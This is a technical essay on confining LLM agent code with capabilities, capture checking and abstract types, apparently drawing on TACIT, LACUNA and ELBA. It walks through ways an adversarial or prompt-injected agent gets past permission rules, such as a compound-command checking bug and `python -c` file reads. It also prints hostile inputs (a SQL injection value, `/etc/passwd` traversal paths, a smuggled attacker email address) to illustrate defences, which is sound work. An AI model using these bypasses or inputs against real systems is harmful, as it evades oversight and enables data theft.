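Exceptions can carry capabilities to code that should not have them. Suppose a trusted function passes a private file to a helper, and the helper throws an exception containing the file. If the trusted function does not catch the exception, its caller receives the file, and that caller may be the attacker. Joe-E prevents this by requiring exceptions to contain only immutable data. Scala's safe mode similarly forbids capabilities as fields of exceptions.

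An exception can also leak information just by occurring. If agent code divides by zero when a secret begins with the letter A, an observer who sees the failure can infer the first letter. Odersky and colleagues considered banning exceptions but rejected the idea as impractical. Division by zero, stack overflow and memory exhaustion can all cause exceptions, so a compiler that ruled out every possible exception would reject nearly all useful code.

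Agent functions instead contain exceptions at run time by returning a `Try`, a standard Scala type that holds either a result or a failure. The failure is then an ordinary value, which the library can seal in the same protective wrapper as the secret. Scala 3 implements early returns, loop breaks and continuations as exceptions, so this covers them too. However, it does not repair an object that an exception left half-updated, which is the problem behind Joe-E's ban on catching errors.

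### Subsets, interpreters and new languages

A subset of a popular language keeps that language's tools, and models have already been trained on a lot of code in it. But its designers must find and exclude every dangerous feature of the full language. Attempts to confine ordinary Python or JavaScript from inside the language have a poor record for this reason. Removing the dangerous names is not enough, because code in both languages can often start from a harmless-looking object and follow its attributes to powerful parts of the runtime.

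A restricted interpreter supports only the features its developers add, so a feature they forget is missing rather than dangerous. Monty, a Python interpreter written in Rust to run code in isolation, is one example. VirtusLab describes a similar property of WebAssembly, a portable format for compiled code, whose modules cannot access files or the network unless the host provides access. But restricted interpreters usually support less of the language. CaMeL, a defence against prompt injection that uses its own Python interpreter, does not let agents define functions. Zhao and colleagues also object that restricted interpreters limit code only while it runs, without first checking the whole action.

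A new language can be safe from the start because no existing programs depend on unsafe features. Modula-3, a research language from the 1980s, made modules safe by default. Terei and colleagues wanted something similar for Haskell but dropped the idea because it would have broken too much existing code. ETAS is a new language for agents. The main argument against creating a new language comes from Odersky and colleagues, who say that people must be able to read and edit agent code and that models need human-written examples to learn from. At first, a new language has few programmers who know it and few such examples.

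For an agent that only calculates or reshapes data, a restricted interpreter is probably the simplest choice. A subset of a typed language makes more sense when the agent acts on real resources, since a mistake found halfway through a run may do real harm. A new language is hard to justify unless it offers protection that neither of these can provide.

### The end of Java's Security Manager

Java's original protection against untrusted code checked privileges at run time instead of restricting the language. Each class had privileges that depended on where its code came from. Before a sensitive operation such as opening a file, the library called the Security Manager, which searched back through the chain of function calls in progress. If it reached a function that had enabled the necessary privilege, the operation went ahead, but if it reached untrusted code first, it threw an exception.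 These checks slowed programs by up to 9%, according to Terei and colleagues.

The design relied on library authors to request a check before every sensitive operation. If they forgot one, any code could perform that operation. With Joe-E's list, by contrast, a method that nobody has reviewed is unavailable.

Java's maintainers deprecated the Security Manager in 2021 and permanently disabled it in JDK 24, released in 2025. Few applications still used it, but they had to maintain its checks throughout the standard library. Safe Haskell was nearly removed for much the same reason. Scala's safe mode is experimental and could also be removed, so a team that builds on it should have a second layer of protection and a plan for replacing safe mode.

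### A checklist for judging a subset

Before trusting a subset with an adversarial agent's code, a builder should be able to answer these questions:

- Is a new language feature or library method unavailable until someone approves it? If it is available until someone bans it, who checks each release?
- Can the source file switch the checks off? The setting should be on the command line or in a tool that the agent cannot edit.
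- Who reviewed each permitted library method, and did they try unusual inputs such as null?
- Can the agent mark its own code as trusted, either in a snippet or in a file it proposes for merging?
- What can run during compilation, and does a sandbox contain it?
- Can code keep data in a global variable between one call and the next?
- What can an exception carry, and which code can run after memory or stack space runs out?
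- Does the check apply to the form of code that the agent submits? Joe-E's verifier reads Java source, and compiled Java files can do things that source code cannot.
- Which guarantees have a proof, and which rest on testing or on the designers' confidence?

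## Granting authority through capabilities

Once agent code cannot bypass the types, its access to the outside world comes from the values that the host program gives it, which the designer has to choose. The `report` function, which counts the lines of a notes file and posts the count, needs one file and one channel. It would work just as well with the whole project folder and an open network connection, but instructions hidden in the notes could then lead the agent to misuse the extra access.

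### Narrowing, withdrawing and delegating access

A host program usually holds more authority than it should pass on. Suppose it has a capability for a project folder. It can take one file from the folder and pass on only that:

```scala
val notes = project.file("notes.txt")
report(notes, team)
```

The function can now use this file and nothing else in the project, as long as the library provides no way to get from a file to its parent folder.

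The host can also narrow what the function may do with the file. `report` only reads, so it has no need for a capability that can write. The wrapper below permits reading and lets the host withdraw access later:

```scala
class Switch:
  var on = true

class LentFile(file: File, switch: Switch):
  def read(): String =
    if switch.on then file.read()
    else throw SecurityException("This access has ended.")
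```

The host creates both objects, gives the agent's code the `LentFile` and keeps the `Switch`. `LentFile` has no `write` operation and keeps `file` private, so the agent's code can only read. When the host sets `switch.on` to false, every later call to `read` fails, even if the agent has passed the `LentFile` to other code.

Withdrawing access cannot take back text that the agent has already read, and it blocks only access that goes through the wrapper. If a wrapped object returns other objects, the wrapper must therefore wrap those too. For example, if a wrapped folder had a `children` operation that returned ordinary files, the agent could collect the files early and keep using them after the host had switched the folder off.

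An agent can narrow its own capabilities in the same way before it delegates work. For example, an agent that serves several customers might start one sub-agent per customer and give each only that customer's records. Odersky and colleagues expect their system to support this, though they have not yet evaluated it with multiple agents. An outer agent would pass on a subset of its capabilities, and the compiler would reject any sub-agent code that needs more. In Zhou and colleagues' Haskell system, a sub-agent's code normally has to meet the same type as its parent's code. The parent can require a stricter type, such as one that allows no effects, but not a looser one, because the parent's own program would then fail to compile.

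With plain object capabilities, it is hard to tell what a returned function can still access. Suppose the sub-agent returns a function of type `() => String`, which takes no input and returns text. In ordinary Scala, this type doesn't show whether the function still has access to a customer's file. The parent might store the function and call it a week later, or pass it to a sub-agent that works for someone else.

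### What a capture set records

Scala 3's capture checking adds this information to types. The type `T^{x}` describes a value of type `T` that may reach the capability `x`. The braces can list several capabilities, and the list is called the capture set. For example, a logger that writes to a file has a type that mentions the file:

```scala
val log: Logger^{file} = Logger(file)
```

The logger's type records `file` even if the logger keeps it in a private field. Function types use a similar notation. A function that takes text and writes it to `file` has the type `String ->{file} Unit`. The type `String -> Unit` describes a pure function, which can reach no capability. The type `String => Unit` describes a function that may reach any capability, and `T^` describes a value of type `T` that may do the same.

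A capture set over-approximates, meaning that it is an upper limit on what a value can reach. The value may never use some of the capabilities listed. Consider this function:

```scala
val keep = (s: String) =>
  if s.length > 1000000 then file.write(s)
```

A function that uses `file` only when its argument is a long enough string has type `String ->{file} Unit`, even if it never receives such a string. The compiler doesn't have the strings, so it must assume that the function may use `file`. Wrapping the code in an object would not hide the file either, because an object's capture set includes whatever its methods use.

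Capture sets also determine which values can stand in for others. The notation `A <: B` means that a value of type `A` is acceptable wherever the program requires a `B`. Odersky and colleagues give this chain, here with the names from the logger example:

```scala
A  <:  A^{log}  <:  A^{log, file}  <:  A^
```

A value that can reach less is acceptable in more places. If a program asks for a function that may use the notes file and nothing else, written `String ->{notes} String`, the compiler decides as follows:

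| Type of the function the agent supplies | What it may reach | Accepted? |
|---|---|---|
| `String -> String` | Nothing | Yes |
| `String ->{notes} String` | The notes file | Yes |
| `String ->{notes, team} String` | The notes file and the channel | No |
| `String => String` | Anything | No |

The rule sometimes rejects harmless code. In one of Odersky and colleagues' test runs, an agent wrote a helper function that printed the first five lines of a file. It declared the input as `FileEntry`, the library's type for a file, without the `^`. That type describes a file object that can reach no capability, but the agent's files could all reach the file system, so the compiler rejected the call. Declaring the input as `FileEntry^` would normally fix this kind of error.

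### Why a file system cannot leave its block

TACIT, the system that Odersky and colleagues built, uses capture sets to limit how long agent code keeps a capability. To reach files, the code calls a library function with this signature, slightly simplified:

```scala
def requestFileSystem[T](root: String)
    (block: FileSystem^ => T): T
```

The caller names a folder and supplies a block of code. The library creates a `FileSystem` capability for that folder, passes it to the block, and invalidates it when the block finishes. The caller gets back the block's result, and `T` stands for the type of that result.

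The compiler accepts this program:

```scala
val count = requestFileSystem("/work/notes"): fs =>
  val f    = fs.access("june.txt")
  val text = f.read()
  text.split("\n").length
```

1. The first line opens the block and gives the new capability the name `fs`.
2. The second line gets a file. Its type is `FileEntry^{fs}`, since the file is usable only through `fs`.
3. The third line reads the file. The result is a plain `String`, which reaches no capability.
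4. The last line counts the lines, so the block's result is a whole number and `T` is `Int`. This type mentions nothing from inside the block, and the number can leave.

The next program differs only in what it returns, and the compiler rejects it:

```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/work/notes"): fs =>
  val f = fs.access("june.txt")
  () => f.read()
later()
```

1. The first line again creates `fs`.
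2. The second line again gives `f` the type `FileEntry^{fs}`.
3. The third line doesn't read the file. It builds a function that would read it on demand. This function is a closure, meaning that it holds on to a variable from the code around it, and its type is `() ->{f} String`.
4. To return the closure, the compiler would have to use that type for `T`. But `T` belongs to the caller, outside the block, where neither `f` nor `fs` exists. No valid choice of `T` remains, so the compiler rejects the program before it opens any file. The call to `later()` on the last line never happens.

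The agent cannot get around this restriction by explicitly writing the type `() => String`, even though that type allows any capability and so should fit a closure that reaches `f`. In a block's result type, "any capability" covers only those that exist outside the block. Zhao and colleagues show a similar case, in which a block creates an input/output capability and its result type is written out as `String => String`. The compiler rejects the closure with a message that the capability "outlives its scope".

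The same rule stops agent code from passing a capability out of its block in a list or an outside variable. In one recorded run, an agent tried to return a list of file objects from its block, probably just to use them in the next step, and the compiler rejected the code. In a multi-turn conversation, every block from an earlier turn has already ended, so the agent has to request access again.

A host can limit how long an agent holds a capability with a scoped block, a revocable wrapper, or both. The block's end is fixed in the program text, so the compiler can reject code that would use the capability after that point. But the host can't end the block early in response to events, such as an administrator noticing something odd halfway through. A revocable wrapper lets the host withdraw the capability at that moment, though the withdrawal shows up in the agent's code only when a call fails.

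Neither one restricts ordinary data. The accepted program could have returned `text` instead of the line count, and the whole file would have left the block as an ordinary `String`. Preventing this requires a different mechanism, such as the sealed `Classified` type that TACIT uses for confidential text.

### The names in scope as a permission set

In LACUNA, a model fills typed gaps in a running program, and the developer grants authority by choosing where to put each call to the model. A call has the form `agent[T](task)`, where `task` is the instruction and `T` is the type of the result. The model also receives the surrounding source code and a list of the available variables with their types. The compiler checks the model's code at the location of the call, so the code can use exactly the names that a developer could have used there. Zhao and colleagues treat those names as the agent's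 permission set.

A developer can use this to give each phase of a task different powers:

```scala
def summarise(notes: File^): String =
  agent[String]("Summarise the notes in three sentences.")

def announce(summary: String, team: Channel^): Unit =
  agent[Unit]("Post the summary to the team.")
```

Inside `summarise`, the snippet can read the notes but has no channel. If it contains `team.send(...)`, the compiler rejects it because it cannot find `team`. Inside `announce`, the snippet can post a message but cannot open the file. (The split does not stop the first snippet from returning the entire file as its "summary", which the other would then post.)

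A rejected snippet does not run, so the account balance in Zhao and colleagues' example stayed at 100. If the model uses up its retries, the call throws an exception containing the compiler's last error messages, and the surrounding program can catch it and do something else. This is the right outcome when the task requires a power that the developer didn't grant. However, code that catches this exception also catches failures from calls nested inside the snippet, even if those failures are unrelated to the main task. A variant called `agentSafe` avoids this by returning the failure as an ordinary value.

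Nesting makes permissions harder to track. A snippet may itself call `agent`, and the nested call can use everything its parent could, plus any variables the parent's snippet has introduced. To give a sub-agent less, the developer puts the call in a separate top-level function and passes in only what the sub-agent should have:

```scala
def subAgent[T](prompt: String): T =
  agent[T](prompt)
```

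Sub-agents here cannot access the caller's local variables, but they can still access the file's top-level imports and definitions. If the developer has defined a database connection there for convenience, every sub-agent in the file can refer to it.

### File paths that code cannot forge

Zhou and colleagues control file access in Haskell through values of a type called `Path`. The type's constructor is private to the library, so the only way to get a `Path` is to receive one or to narrow one that the program already has. The operator `//` does the narrowing:

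```haskell
copyNotes :: Path -> RIO ()
copyNotes folder = do
  text <- readRIO (folder // "june.txt")
  writeRIO (folder // "copy.txt") text
```

`RIO` marks a program that may use files only through this library. An agent that writes `readRIO "/etc/passwd"` gets a type error, because a string is not a `Path`.

The compiler cannot catch `folder // "../../etc/passwd"` because both parts have the right types, and whether the result lies inside the folder depends on the disk. Even `june.txt` might be a symbolic link, a file that redirects to another location, and someone might create the link after the code has compiled. The `//` operator therefore resolves the path at run time, following any links, and fails if the result lies outside the folder. TACIT also checks at run time that each path lies under the requested root.

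These runtime checks weaken the all-or-nothing property. If a snippet writes two files and then tries to escape from its folder, the escape fails but the two files remain. A designer who needs all-or-nothing behavior must provide it separately, for example by letting the agent work on a copy. A library of this kind should also check a file's location and open it in the same step, because otherwise another process could swap in a link between the check and the read.

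Haskell's `RIO` type is less specific than a Scala capture set. It shows that a program may use files, while a Scala type such as `String ->{notes} Unit` shows which file. `RIO` may be enough for someone who only wants to keep an agent inside one folder, and it needs no experimental compiler feature.

Operating-system sandboxes can also confine a program to certain folders. Zhou and colleagues regard sandboxes and capabilities as complementary. They point out that a sandbox fixes its list of folders for the whole process, while a program can create, pass on and narrow `Path` values as it runs. Capabilities can also represent things that have no operating-system equivalent, such as all the files on one branch of a version-control repository.

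### Rules that match command strings

Many coding agents act by running shell commands, and their permission systems compare the text of each command with a list of patterns. Rules might allow commands that start with `git status` and forbid those that start with `rm`. If no rule applies, the system prompts the user.

Zhou and colleagues object that such rules make the system ask users about commands, when users usually have a policy about files in mind, such as "the agent may change anything in this folder". They give an example of the kind of request Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, shows its users: a single long line that enters a folder six levels deep, changes a timeout from 30 to 60, runs a test script and saves the output to a dated log. A user who sees many of these will probably stop reading them. Odersky and colleagues make the same complaint about confirmation requests in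 general.

Matching strings is also fragile. In March 2026, a faulty update to Claude Code caused it to check only the first part of a compound command. The shell runs commands joined by `&&` one after another, so an attacker could place a forbidden command behind a permitted one. Better parsing would fix that bug, but it would not help with this command:

```
python -c "open('denied.txt').read()"
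```

The only shell command here is `python`. The rest is a program in another language, and a pattern written for shell commands can't determine what that program does. An attacker could assemble the file name from pieces, as in the earlier example with the word `delete`.

With capabilities, users grant permission for a file or folder. Code that has no capability for `denied.txt` can't open it, however the request is written.

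String rules have the practical advantage of working with every existing command-line tool. Capabilities cover only code in the host language, so the old problem returns once an agent is allowed to start outside programs. In TACIT, agent code requests a list of permitted commands with `requestExecPermission`, and an example in the library's documentation requests `pip` and `python`. An agent with that permission can run the command above. TACIT has a strict mode that also blocks file commands such as `cat` and `rm`, but a general-purpose interpreter on the list can do everything they do. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that their static guarantee does not extend to such commands, and recommend permitting only specific safe ones.

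### Modules and dependencies

A snippet needs its permissions for a few seconds, but if an agent contributes a module to a long-lived program, people will want to know years later what the module can do, without reading all of it.

Wyvern, a research language, builds capabilities into its module system. A module that needs files or the network must receive them as parameters from the code that loads it. If an agent contributes a spreadsheet parser that takes no such parameters, a reviewer knows without reading its 2,000 lines that it can't open a network connection. A later version that sends usage statistics would need a new parameter, and every program that loads the module would have to change to supply it.

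Passing everything as parameters can be a burden. In a traditional capability system, the program's entry point receives all capabilities from the host and passes them down through every function that needs them, which usually means restructuring an existing codebase. Scala's capture checking permits global capabilities instead, because the types record who uses them. Odersky and colleagues give this example:

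```scala
object SimpleLogger uses Console {
  def log(str: String) = Console.out.println(str)
}
```

The `uses` clause is required here because the logger refers to a global object that holds capabilities. Reviewers of agent-written code can also easily monitor this clause for changes. A team could give small changes to a module a light review, but require a person's approval for any change that adds a name to a `uses` clause.

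Most programs also rely on libraries written by strangers, and an agent may add new ones with little scrutiny. In a supply-chain attack, someone hides malicious code in a library that other programs load. Gradient, an extension of Scala published in 2024, defends against this by confining parts of a program to compartments with limited authority. It combines capabilities tracked in types with run-time enforcement, so a team can convert its program one component at a time. Gradual conversion matters because most libraries were written assuming that any code may open any file, and few teams could rewrite them all before getting any protection.

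### Grants that are too broad

The compiler enforces whatever grant the developer makes, even one that is too broad. Zhao and colleagues state that their type system does not work out the smallest set of permissions for a task. If a developer leaves a network connection in scope for a task that only reads files, an injected instruction can use it, and the code will still compile. The access token in the PocketOS incident was also broader than its task required.

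Agents that choose their own grants can request more access than they need. In TACIT, the agent's code names the folder it wants. One of the recorded snippets requests `"."`, the entire current folder, although it only looks at Scala files in a subfolder called `sample-data`. This was presumably for convenience, but an adversarial programmer could just as easily request the root of the disk. A deployment therefore needs an upper limit that the agent's code cannot raise, such as a version of `requestFileSystem` that refuses any folder outside the project. ATC, a coding agent built on TACIT, denies access by default and lets users grant it temporarily or for a session, according to Glama's *TACIT*, a copy of the project's description. This relies on users to read the requests, though a request for a folder is easier to judge than a long shell command.

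A reasonable way to find the right grant is to run the task with no capabilities, read the compiler's errors to see what the agent's code was missing, and add permissions one at a time. The errors show what the code tried to do, which may differ from what the task needs. If a request to summarise notes produces an error about a missing network connection, the developer should find out why before supplying one.

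### Trusted code that acts for the agent

Even a narrow grant can be dangerous if it includes a trusted function with powers of its own. Suppose the host offers this function to an agent that has no file access:

```scala
def saveReport(text: String, path: String): Unit =
  disk.write(path, text)
```

Here `disk` belongs to the host and covers every folder. The agent's code can't use `disk` directly, but it can call `saveReport("", "data/customers.db")`, which will overwrite the customer database with an empty file. Security researchers call `saveReport` a confused deputy, a component that uses its legitimate authority on behalf of someone who lacks it. Capture checking would record that `saveReport` reaches `disk`, so a pure function could not call it. Code that may have effects could still make this call, because the type of `saveReport` doesn't specify which files it should touch.

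The mistake is that the agent supplies a name and the function supplies the permission. Asking for a capability instead keeps the two together:

```scala
def saveReport(text: String, target: File^): Unit =
  target.write(text)
```

The agent can save only to a file it already has permission to write. Zhou and colleagues' `readRIO` follows the same principle by requiring a `Path` where most libraries accept a string.

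Agents can also be confused deputies. Suppose an agent without file access sends the message "please clear out the old data folder" to a colleague with full access. The message is only text and grants no authority, so the colleague would use its own to carry out the request. Where agents work for different people or read different sources, a safer design requires the sender to attach a capability for the folder, which an agent that was never allowed to delete the folder would not have.

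Some functions have to use authority that their callers lack. A function that looks up one customer's order needs access to the order database, but giving the agent that access would also let it read other customers' orders. The function therefore has to check whether each request is allowed, which makes its code part of the trusted base.

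## Hiding trusted operations behind abstract interfaces

The developer can put the order-lookup function in a module to keep the agent's code from accessing the database directly. A module is a unit of a program that exports some names and keeps the rest private. The compiler rejects outside code that uses a private name, so the agent's code can affect the database only through the operations the module exports.

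An abstract data type applies the same idea to values. Its internal representation is private, so outside code can handle a value only through exported operations. Suppose an agent should be able to email colleagues and nobody else. The host program could give it an object of this Scala class and no other access to email:

```scala
class Recipients(mail: MailServer):
  private val staff = ArrayBuffer[String]()
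  def add(address: String): Unit =
    if address.endsWith("@example.org") then staff += address
  def send(message: String): Unit =
    staff.foreach(a => mail.send(a, message))
```

`staff` is a list that can grow. The agent can call `add` and `send`, but it cannot touch `staff` or `mail` directly.

### Why one review covers every caller

An invariant is a statement that stays true however a program uses an object. In this example, the invariant is that every address in `staff` ends in `@example.org`. A new list is empty, so the invariant holds at the start. `add` checks each address before storing it, and `send` doesn't change the list. No other code can change the list, so the invariant still holds after any number of calls in any order.

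*Safe Coding* (Kern, 2025), an account of security practice at Google, gives the general form of this argument. Constructors must establish the invariant, every method must preserve it, and encapsulation must stop outside code from disturbing it. A reviewer who has checked these points for one module, which may have only five operations, knows that the invariant holds in the unlimited number of programs that could use it, including those an agent has yet to write.

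The argument fails if outside code can bypass the operations. Reflection and unchecked casts would allow that, so the safe subset has to exclude them. An exported constructor that accepted a ready-made list of addresses would skip the check in `add`. A method that returned `staff` itself would let the agent add an outside address to the real list. Returning a copy would be safe if the addresses are not secret.

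The risk from callbacks is easier to miss. Suppose the class also had a method that applied a function supplied by the agent to every address, stored each result, and then removed any that failed the check. The agent's function could call `send` partway through, while an outside address was still in the list.

Even an invariant that always holds may be too weak to enforce the policy. Here the policy restricts who receives the message, but the reviewer has proved only that the text ends in `@example.org`. `add` therefore accepts `eve@attacker.net,bob@example.org`, and if the mail server treats commas as separators, the message goes to both people.

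### A library for the bibliography agent

For the bibliography agent, whose entries must all come from DBLP, Zhou and colleagues provide a library with three operations:

```haskell
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: FilePath -> Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

In Haskell, `::` means "has the type", and the arrows separate inputs from the result. `dblpSearch` takes a search phrase and returns a list of DOIs, which are permanent identifiers for papers. `dblpFetchBib` takes a DOI and returns the matching entry, and `appendToBibFile` adds an entry to a file. The empty parentheses in its type mean it returns no meaningful value.

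`Trusted` is an abstract data type that wraps an entry. Its invariant is that the contents came from DBLP. Only code inside the library can apply the wrapper, and `dblpFetchBib` is the only exported operation that produces a wrapped entry. `appendToBibFile` accepts only wrapped entries.

`Trusted` would be useless if the agent could bypass `appendToBibFile` and write to the file with Haskell's standard `writeFile`. The library therefore defines an effect type, `BibIO`, for programs whose only effects come from these three operations. The developer requires the agent's whole program to have the type `BibIO ()`. This rules out calls to `writeFile`, which has the standard effect type `IO`, the type that permits any input or output.

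The module that defines these types could begin like this:

```haskell
module Bibliography
  ( BibIO, Trusted, Bib, DOI, yearOf
  , dblpSearch, dblpFetchBib, appendToBibFile ) where

newtype Trusted a = Trusted a
newtype BibIO a   = BibIO (IO a)
```

The list in parentheses contains the exports. `yearOf` is an extra function that reads the year from a trusted entry, which is harmless because reading cannot create an entry. Listing `Trusted` exports the type without its constructor. If the developer wrote `Trusted(..)` instead, the module would also export the constructor, and the agent could use it to wrap any text.

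Haskell instances can also remove the protection, less visibly because a module exports them automatically. An instance declares that a type supports a standard set of operations. Haskell programmers often give a custom effect type an instance of `MonadIO`, which converts any `IO` program into the custom type. With that instance, `BibIO` would permit `writeFile`. A `Functor` instance for `Trusted` would let the agent replace the contents of a genuine entry while keeping the wrapper. Both instances are routine conveniences, so a reviewer should look for them specifically.

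### One accepted program and two rejected ones

Asked for the earliest paper on a topic, the agent might write this:

```haskell
do dois    <- dblpSearch "object capabilities"
   entries <- mapM dblpFetchBib dois
   let earliest = minimumBy (comparing yearOf) entries
   appendToBibFile "refs.bib" earliest
```

1. The first line searches DBLP and names the resulting list `dois`.
2. The second line fetches an entry for each DOI. `entries` is a list of values of type `Trusted Bib`.
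3. The third line picks the entry with the lowest year. This is ordinary calculation without effects, so the library needs no special operation for it. The result still has the type `Trusted Bib`, because choosing an item from a list does not change it.
4. The last line writes the entry. Every step with effects has a `BibIO` type, so the whole program has the type `BibIO ()` and the compiler accepts it.

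Now suppose the agent tries to invent an entry:

```haskell
do dois <- dblpSearch "object capabilities"
   writeFile "refs.bib" "@article{smith2019, ...}"
```

The second line has the type `IO ()`, and a `BibIO` program cannot contain an `IO` step, so the compiler rejects the program before the search on the first line runs. If the agent passes the invented text to `appendToBibFile` instead, the compiler rejects that too, because text is not a `Trusted Bib`.

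The agent could still write `undefined`, a Haskell expression that fits every type and crashes when the program needs its value. `appendToBibFile "refs.bib" undefined` compiles but crashes without producing an entry. Zhou and colleagues therefore limit their guarantee to successful output.

ELBA, a Haskell implementation, wrote no invented citations in its developers' tests on 100 topics. The types don't guarantee that an entry is relevant, though, and a DBLP record may contain an error. `appendToBibFile` also takes the file's name as plain text. Unless the function checks that name, an agent could append a genuine entry to a build script and break it. Requiring one of ELBA's `Path` capabilities instead of the name would close this gap.

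### Why not offer a fixed menu of tools?

The fixed tool that fetches and writes an entry in one step also prevents invented entries, and it needs no types. But the agent's code never holds an entry, so to find the earliest of 200 papers, the model must read the dates itself and could misread any of them. The developer could add a tool that finds the earliest paper, but users may also want duplicates removed or only the papers from one conference, and each kind of request would need its own tool. With the typed library, the agent writes the code to sort or filter entries, and the developer reviews only the operations that have effects.

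A fixed set of operations is still a sensible choice for an agent that repeats the same few tasks. It works in any language and doesn't need a compiler.

### How the expected type becomes the policy

ELBA gives developers a single function for calling a model, `agent`:

```haskell
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

`Defs` lists the types and functions that the generated code may use, and `Prompt` contains the instructions. The result type `t` can be any type, depending on where the developer puts the call. ELBA sends the model this type, the prompt and the definitions, then checks the returned program against the type. Retries work as in LACUNA, and a Haskell interpreter runs the program once it passes.

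The developer therefore sets the policy by choosing the type:

| Expected type | What an accepted program can do |
|---|---|
| `Int` | Calculate a whole number, with no tool calls |
| `BibIO ()` | Use the three library operations and any calculation |
| `BibIO (Trusted Bib)` | The same, and it must return an entry from DBLP |
| `IO ()` | Anything the surrounding process can do |

This differs from LACUNA, where the names in scope form the permission set. In ELBA, carelessly adding `writeFile` to the definitions does no damage as long as the expected type is `BibIO ()`, because `writeFile` has the wrong type. Adding a dangerous function with a `BibIO` type would do damage, so the developer must still review everything that can produce that effect.

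Haskell can often infer the expected type of a call from the surrounding code. Zhou and colleagues give the example of a call that parses dates before a function sorts them by year. The compiler infers that the call must return a `Date`, and ELBA passes this type to the model, so the prompt can be "parse this". Inference is riskier for effects. If a developer places a call inside an ordinary `IO` program without writing a type, the compiler may infer `IO ()`, which does not restrict the call's effects. Developers should therefore write out the type of any call with effects, where a reviewer can see it.

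### Why a sub-agent cannot gain power

`agent` generates one complete program per call, but many tasks require the model to look at a result before deciding what to do next. The generated program can do this by calling `agent` itself:

```haskell
do dois <- dblpSearch "object capabilities"
   agent bibTools ("Refine this search or write the file. "
                   ++ "First result: " ++ show (take 1 dois))
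```

The call on the second line is a step in a `BibIO` program, so the compiler infers that its result must also have a `BibIO` type. A sub-agent therefore inherits its parent's policy without anyone restating it.

If the parent requests a `String` instead, the sub-agent has to suggest a better search phrase without calling any tools. Requesting a looser type doesn't help the parent, because even if the parent stores a sub-agent's `IO ()` program in a variable, `BibIO` has no operation to run it.

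These types do not record the effect of calling `agent`, which sends its prompt to a language model, usually over a network. The call's type can be a plain `Int`, so code that looks pure may pass text to the model's provider. That would be a problem for medical records, but not for a bibliography.

### What the guarantee assumes

Zhou and colleagues prove that adding `agent` to a language preserves the guarantees its types already provide. For a program *e*, traces(*e*) is the set of all sequences of externally visible tool calls that *e* can make. A property *P* belongs to a type *t* if *P*(traces(*e*)) is true for every program *e* of that type. For `BibIO ()`, *P* could be "every entry written came from DBLP". Every such property remains true when programs may contain calls to `agent`.

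The proof treats the model as an arbitrary function that may return any program, so it covers a malicious model. It replaces each call to `agent` with ordinary code that queries the model, checks the answer against *t* and evaluates it. The resulting program is in the original language and has the same type and traces, so the original guarantee applies to it. Generated programs may contain further calls to `agent`, which could make the replacement go on forever. To prevent this, each call has a maximum depth that falls by at least one at every level, and a call at depth zero returns a failure.

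The theorem preserves only the guarantees that the library already provides. If `BibIO` has a stray `MonadIO` instance, *P* is false even for programs that humans write, so the theorem can't guarantee it for generated programs either.

It also assumes that the code around the agent, including its control flow and retry logic, is in the same typed language. Suppose a Python script runs the Haskell program and then asks a model to fill in missing fields in `refs.bib`. That script can put invented data in the file, and no Haskell type will prevent it. Using Haskell throughout is necessary but not sufficient, because every Haskell application starts as an `IO` program that runs the `BibIO` part, and the developer's own `IO` code can call `writeFile` before or after. A developer who wants the provenance rule to cover the whole application should keep the `IO` part very short and review it carefully.

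### Google's experience with human programmers

Google has used abstract types in this way for more than a decade to stop its own programmers from making dangerous mistakes. SQL injection is one such mistake. A program builds a database query by joining text, and some of the text comes from a stranger:

```go
db.Query("SELECT item FROM orders WHERE id = " + input)
```

If `input` is `0 OR 1=1`, the database returns every order. Kern calls `Query` a risky operation, meaning that it is safe only if the programmer first ensures some condition, in this case that no part of the query's text comes from outside the program. Checking this for one call may require reading code in many other files, because the text may have passed through several functions.

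Google's safe version of `Query` accepts only a `TrustedSqlString`. Programmers can build one only from text that appears literally in the program's source code, and they pass outside values such as `input` separately, so the database never treats them as commands. The compiler checks this condition at every call. According to Kern, the hundreds of applications that use these interfaces have had no reported SQL injection vulnerabilities in more than a decade. Some flaws may remain undiscovered, but this is a striking record for such a common type of bug.

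An automatic check also rejects direct uses of risky operations outside modules on an approved list. Experts maintain the list and review each module before adding it. Kern advises them to read the entire module, because any code inside the boundary can break the invariant. The same arrangement would suit an agent that contributes to a long-lived program, if the agent cannot edit the list or the approved modules. Enyedi (2026), in *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age*, goes further and proposes that humans and agents assemble software only from modules that people have certified.

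Kern says safe coding is meant to protect well-meaning programmers from accidents, not to stop malicious ones. A determined programmer could turn any outside text into a `TrustedSqlString` by looking up each character in a table of one-character literals and joining the results. Kern reports that this has not been a significant problem at Google, because such code would look obviously wrong.

An adversarial agent could get around `TrustedSqlString` without the trick, because the type assumes that whoever writes the source code is trustworthy, and here the agent writes it. The agent could write `"DELETE FROM orders"` as a literal, and the safe `Query` would accept it. To prevent this, a builder has to keep the string-building functions away from the agent and export finished queries instead, such as one that lists a given customer's orders. `Trusted Bib` doesn't have this weakness, because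 no exported operation turns the agent's text into a trusted entry.

### Narrowing a refund interface

An interface can hide its representation perfectly and still export an operation that does harm. Consider an agent that handles returns for an online shop and has this function:

```haskell
refund :: OrderId -> Cents -> ShopIO ()
```

The agent cannot reach the payment system any other way, but it can still refund €5,000 on a €50 order, refund an order the customer never sent back, or go through every order number in the shop. A negative amount might charge the customer. All of these calls have the right types, and an agent could make any of them by mistake or because a customer told it to in a message.

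The amount is the easiest to fix. The library already knows what the customer paid, so the agent doesn't need to supply a number. The order of events needs a new abstract type:

```haskell
confirmReturn :: Order -> ShopIO (Maybe Returned)
refund        :: Returned -> ShopIO ()
```

`Maybe Returned` is either a `Returned` value or nothing. `confirmReturn` looks up the order in the warehouse's records and produces a `Returned` value only if the parcel has arrived. No other exported operation creates one, so a program that skips the check has nothing to pass to `refund` and does not compile. `Order` is also abstract. The host supplies one for the order under discussion, and the agent cannot make others by guessing order numbers.

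A `Returned` value shows that the parcel had arrived when the program checked. If the warehouse might correct its records later, `refund` should check again just before paying.

The narrower interface also rules out some useful work, such as refunding €10 for a scratched table that the customer wants to keep. The developer could add an operation for partial refunds with a fixed limit, or send those cases to a person. Adding an operation for every case would recreate the fixed menu, so it makes sense to narrow the operations that move money and leave the agent free to calculate and compare.

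### Tokens that work once

The agent can still pass the new `refund` the same `Returned` value twice, and the shop may pay twice, because ordinary types do not limit how often a program uses a value.

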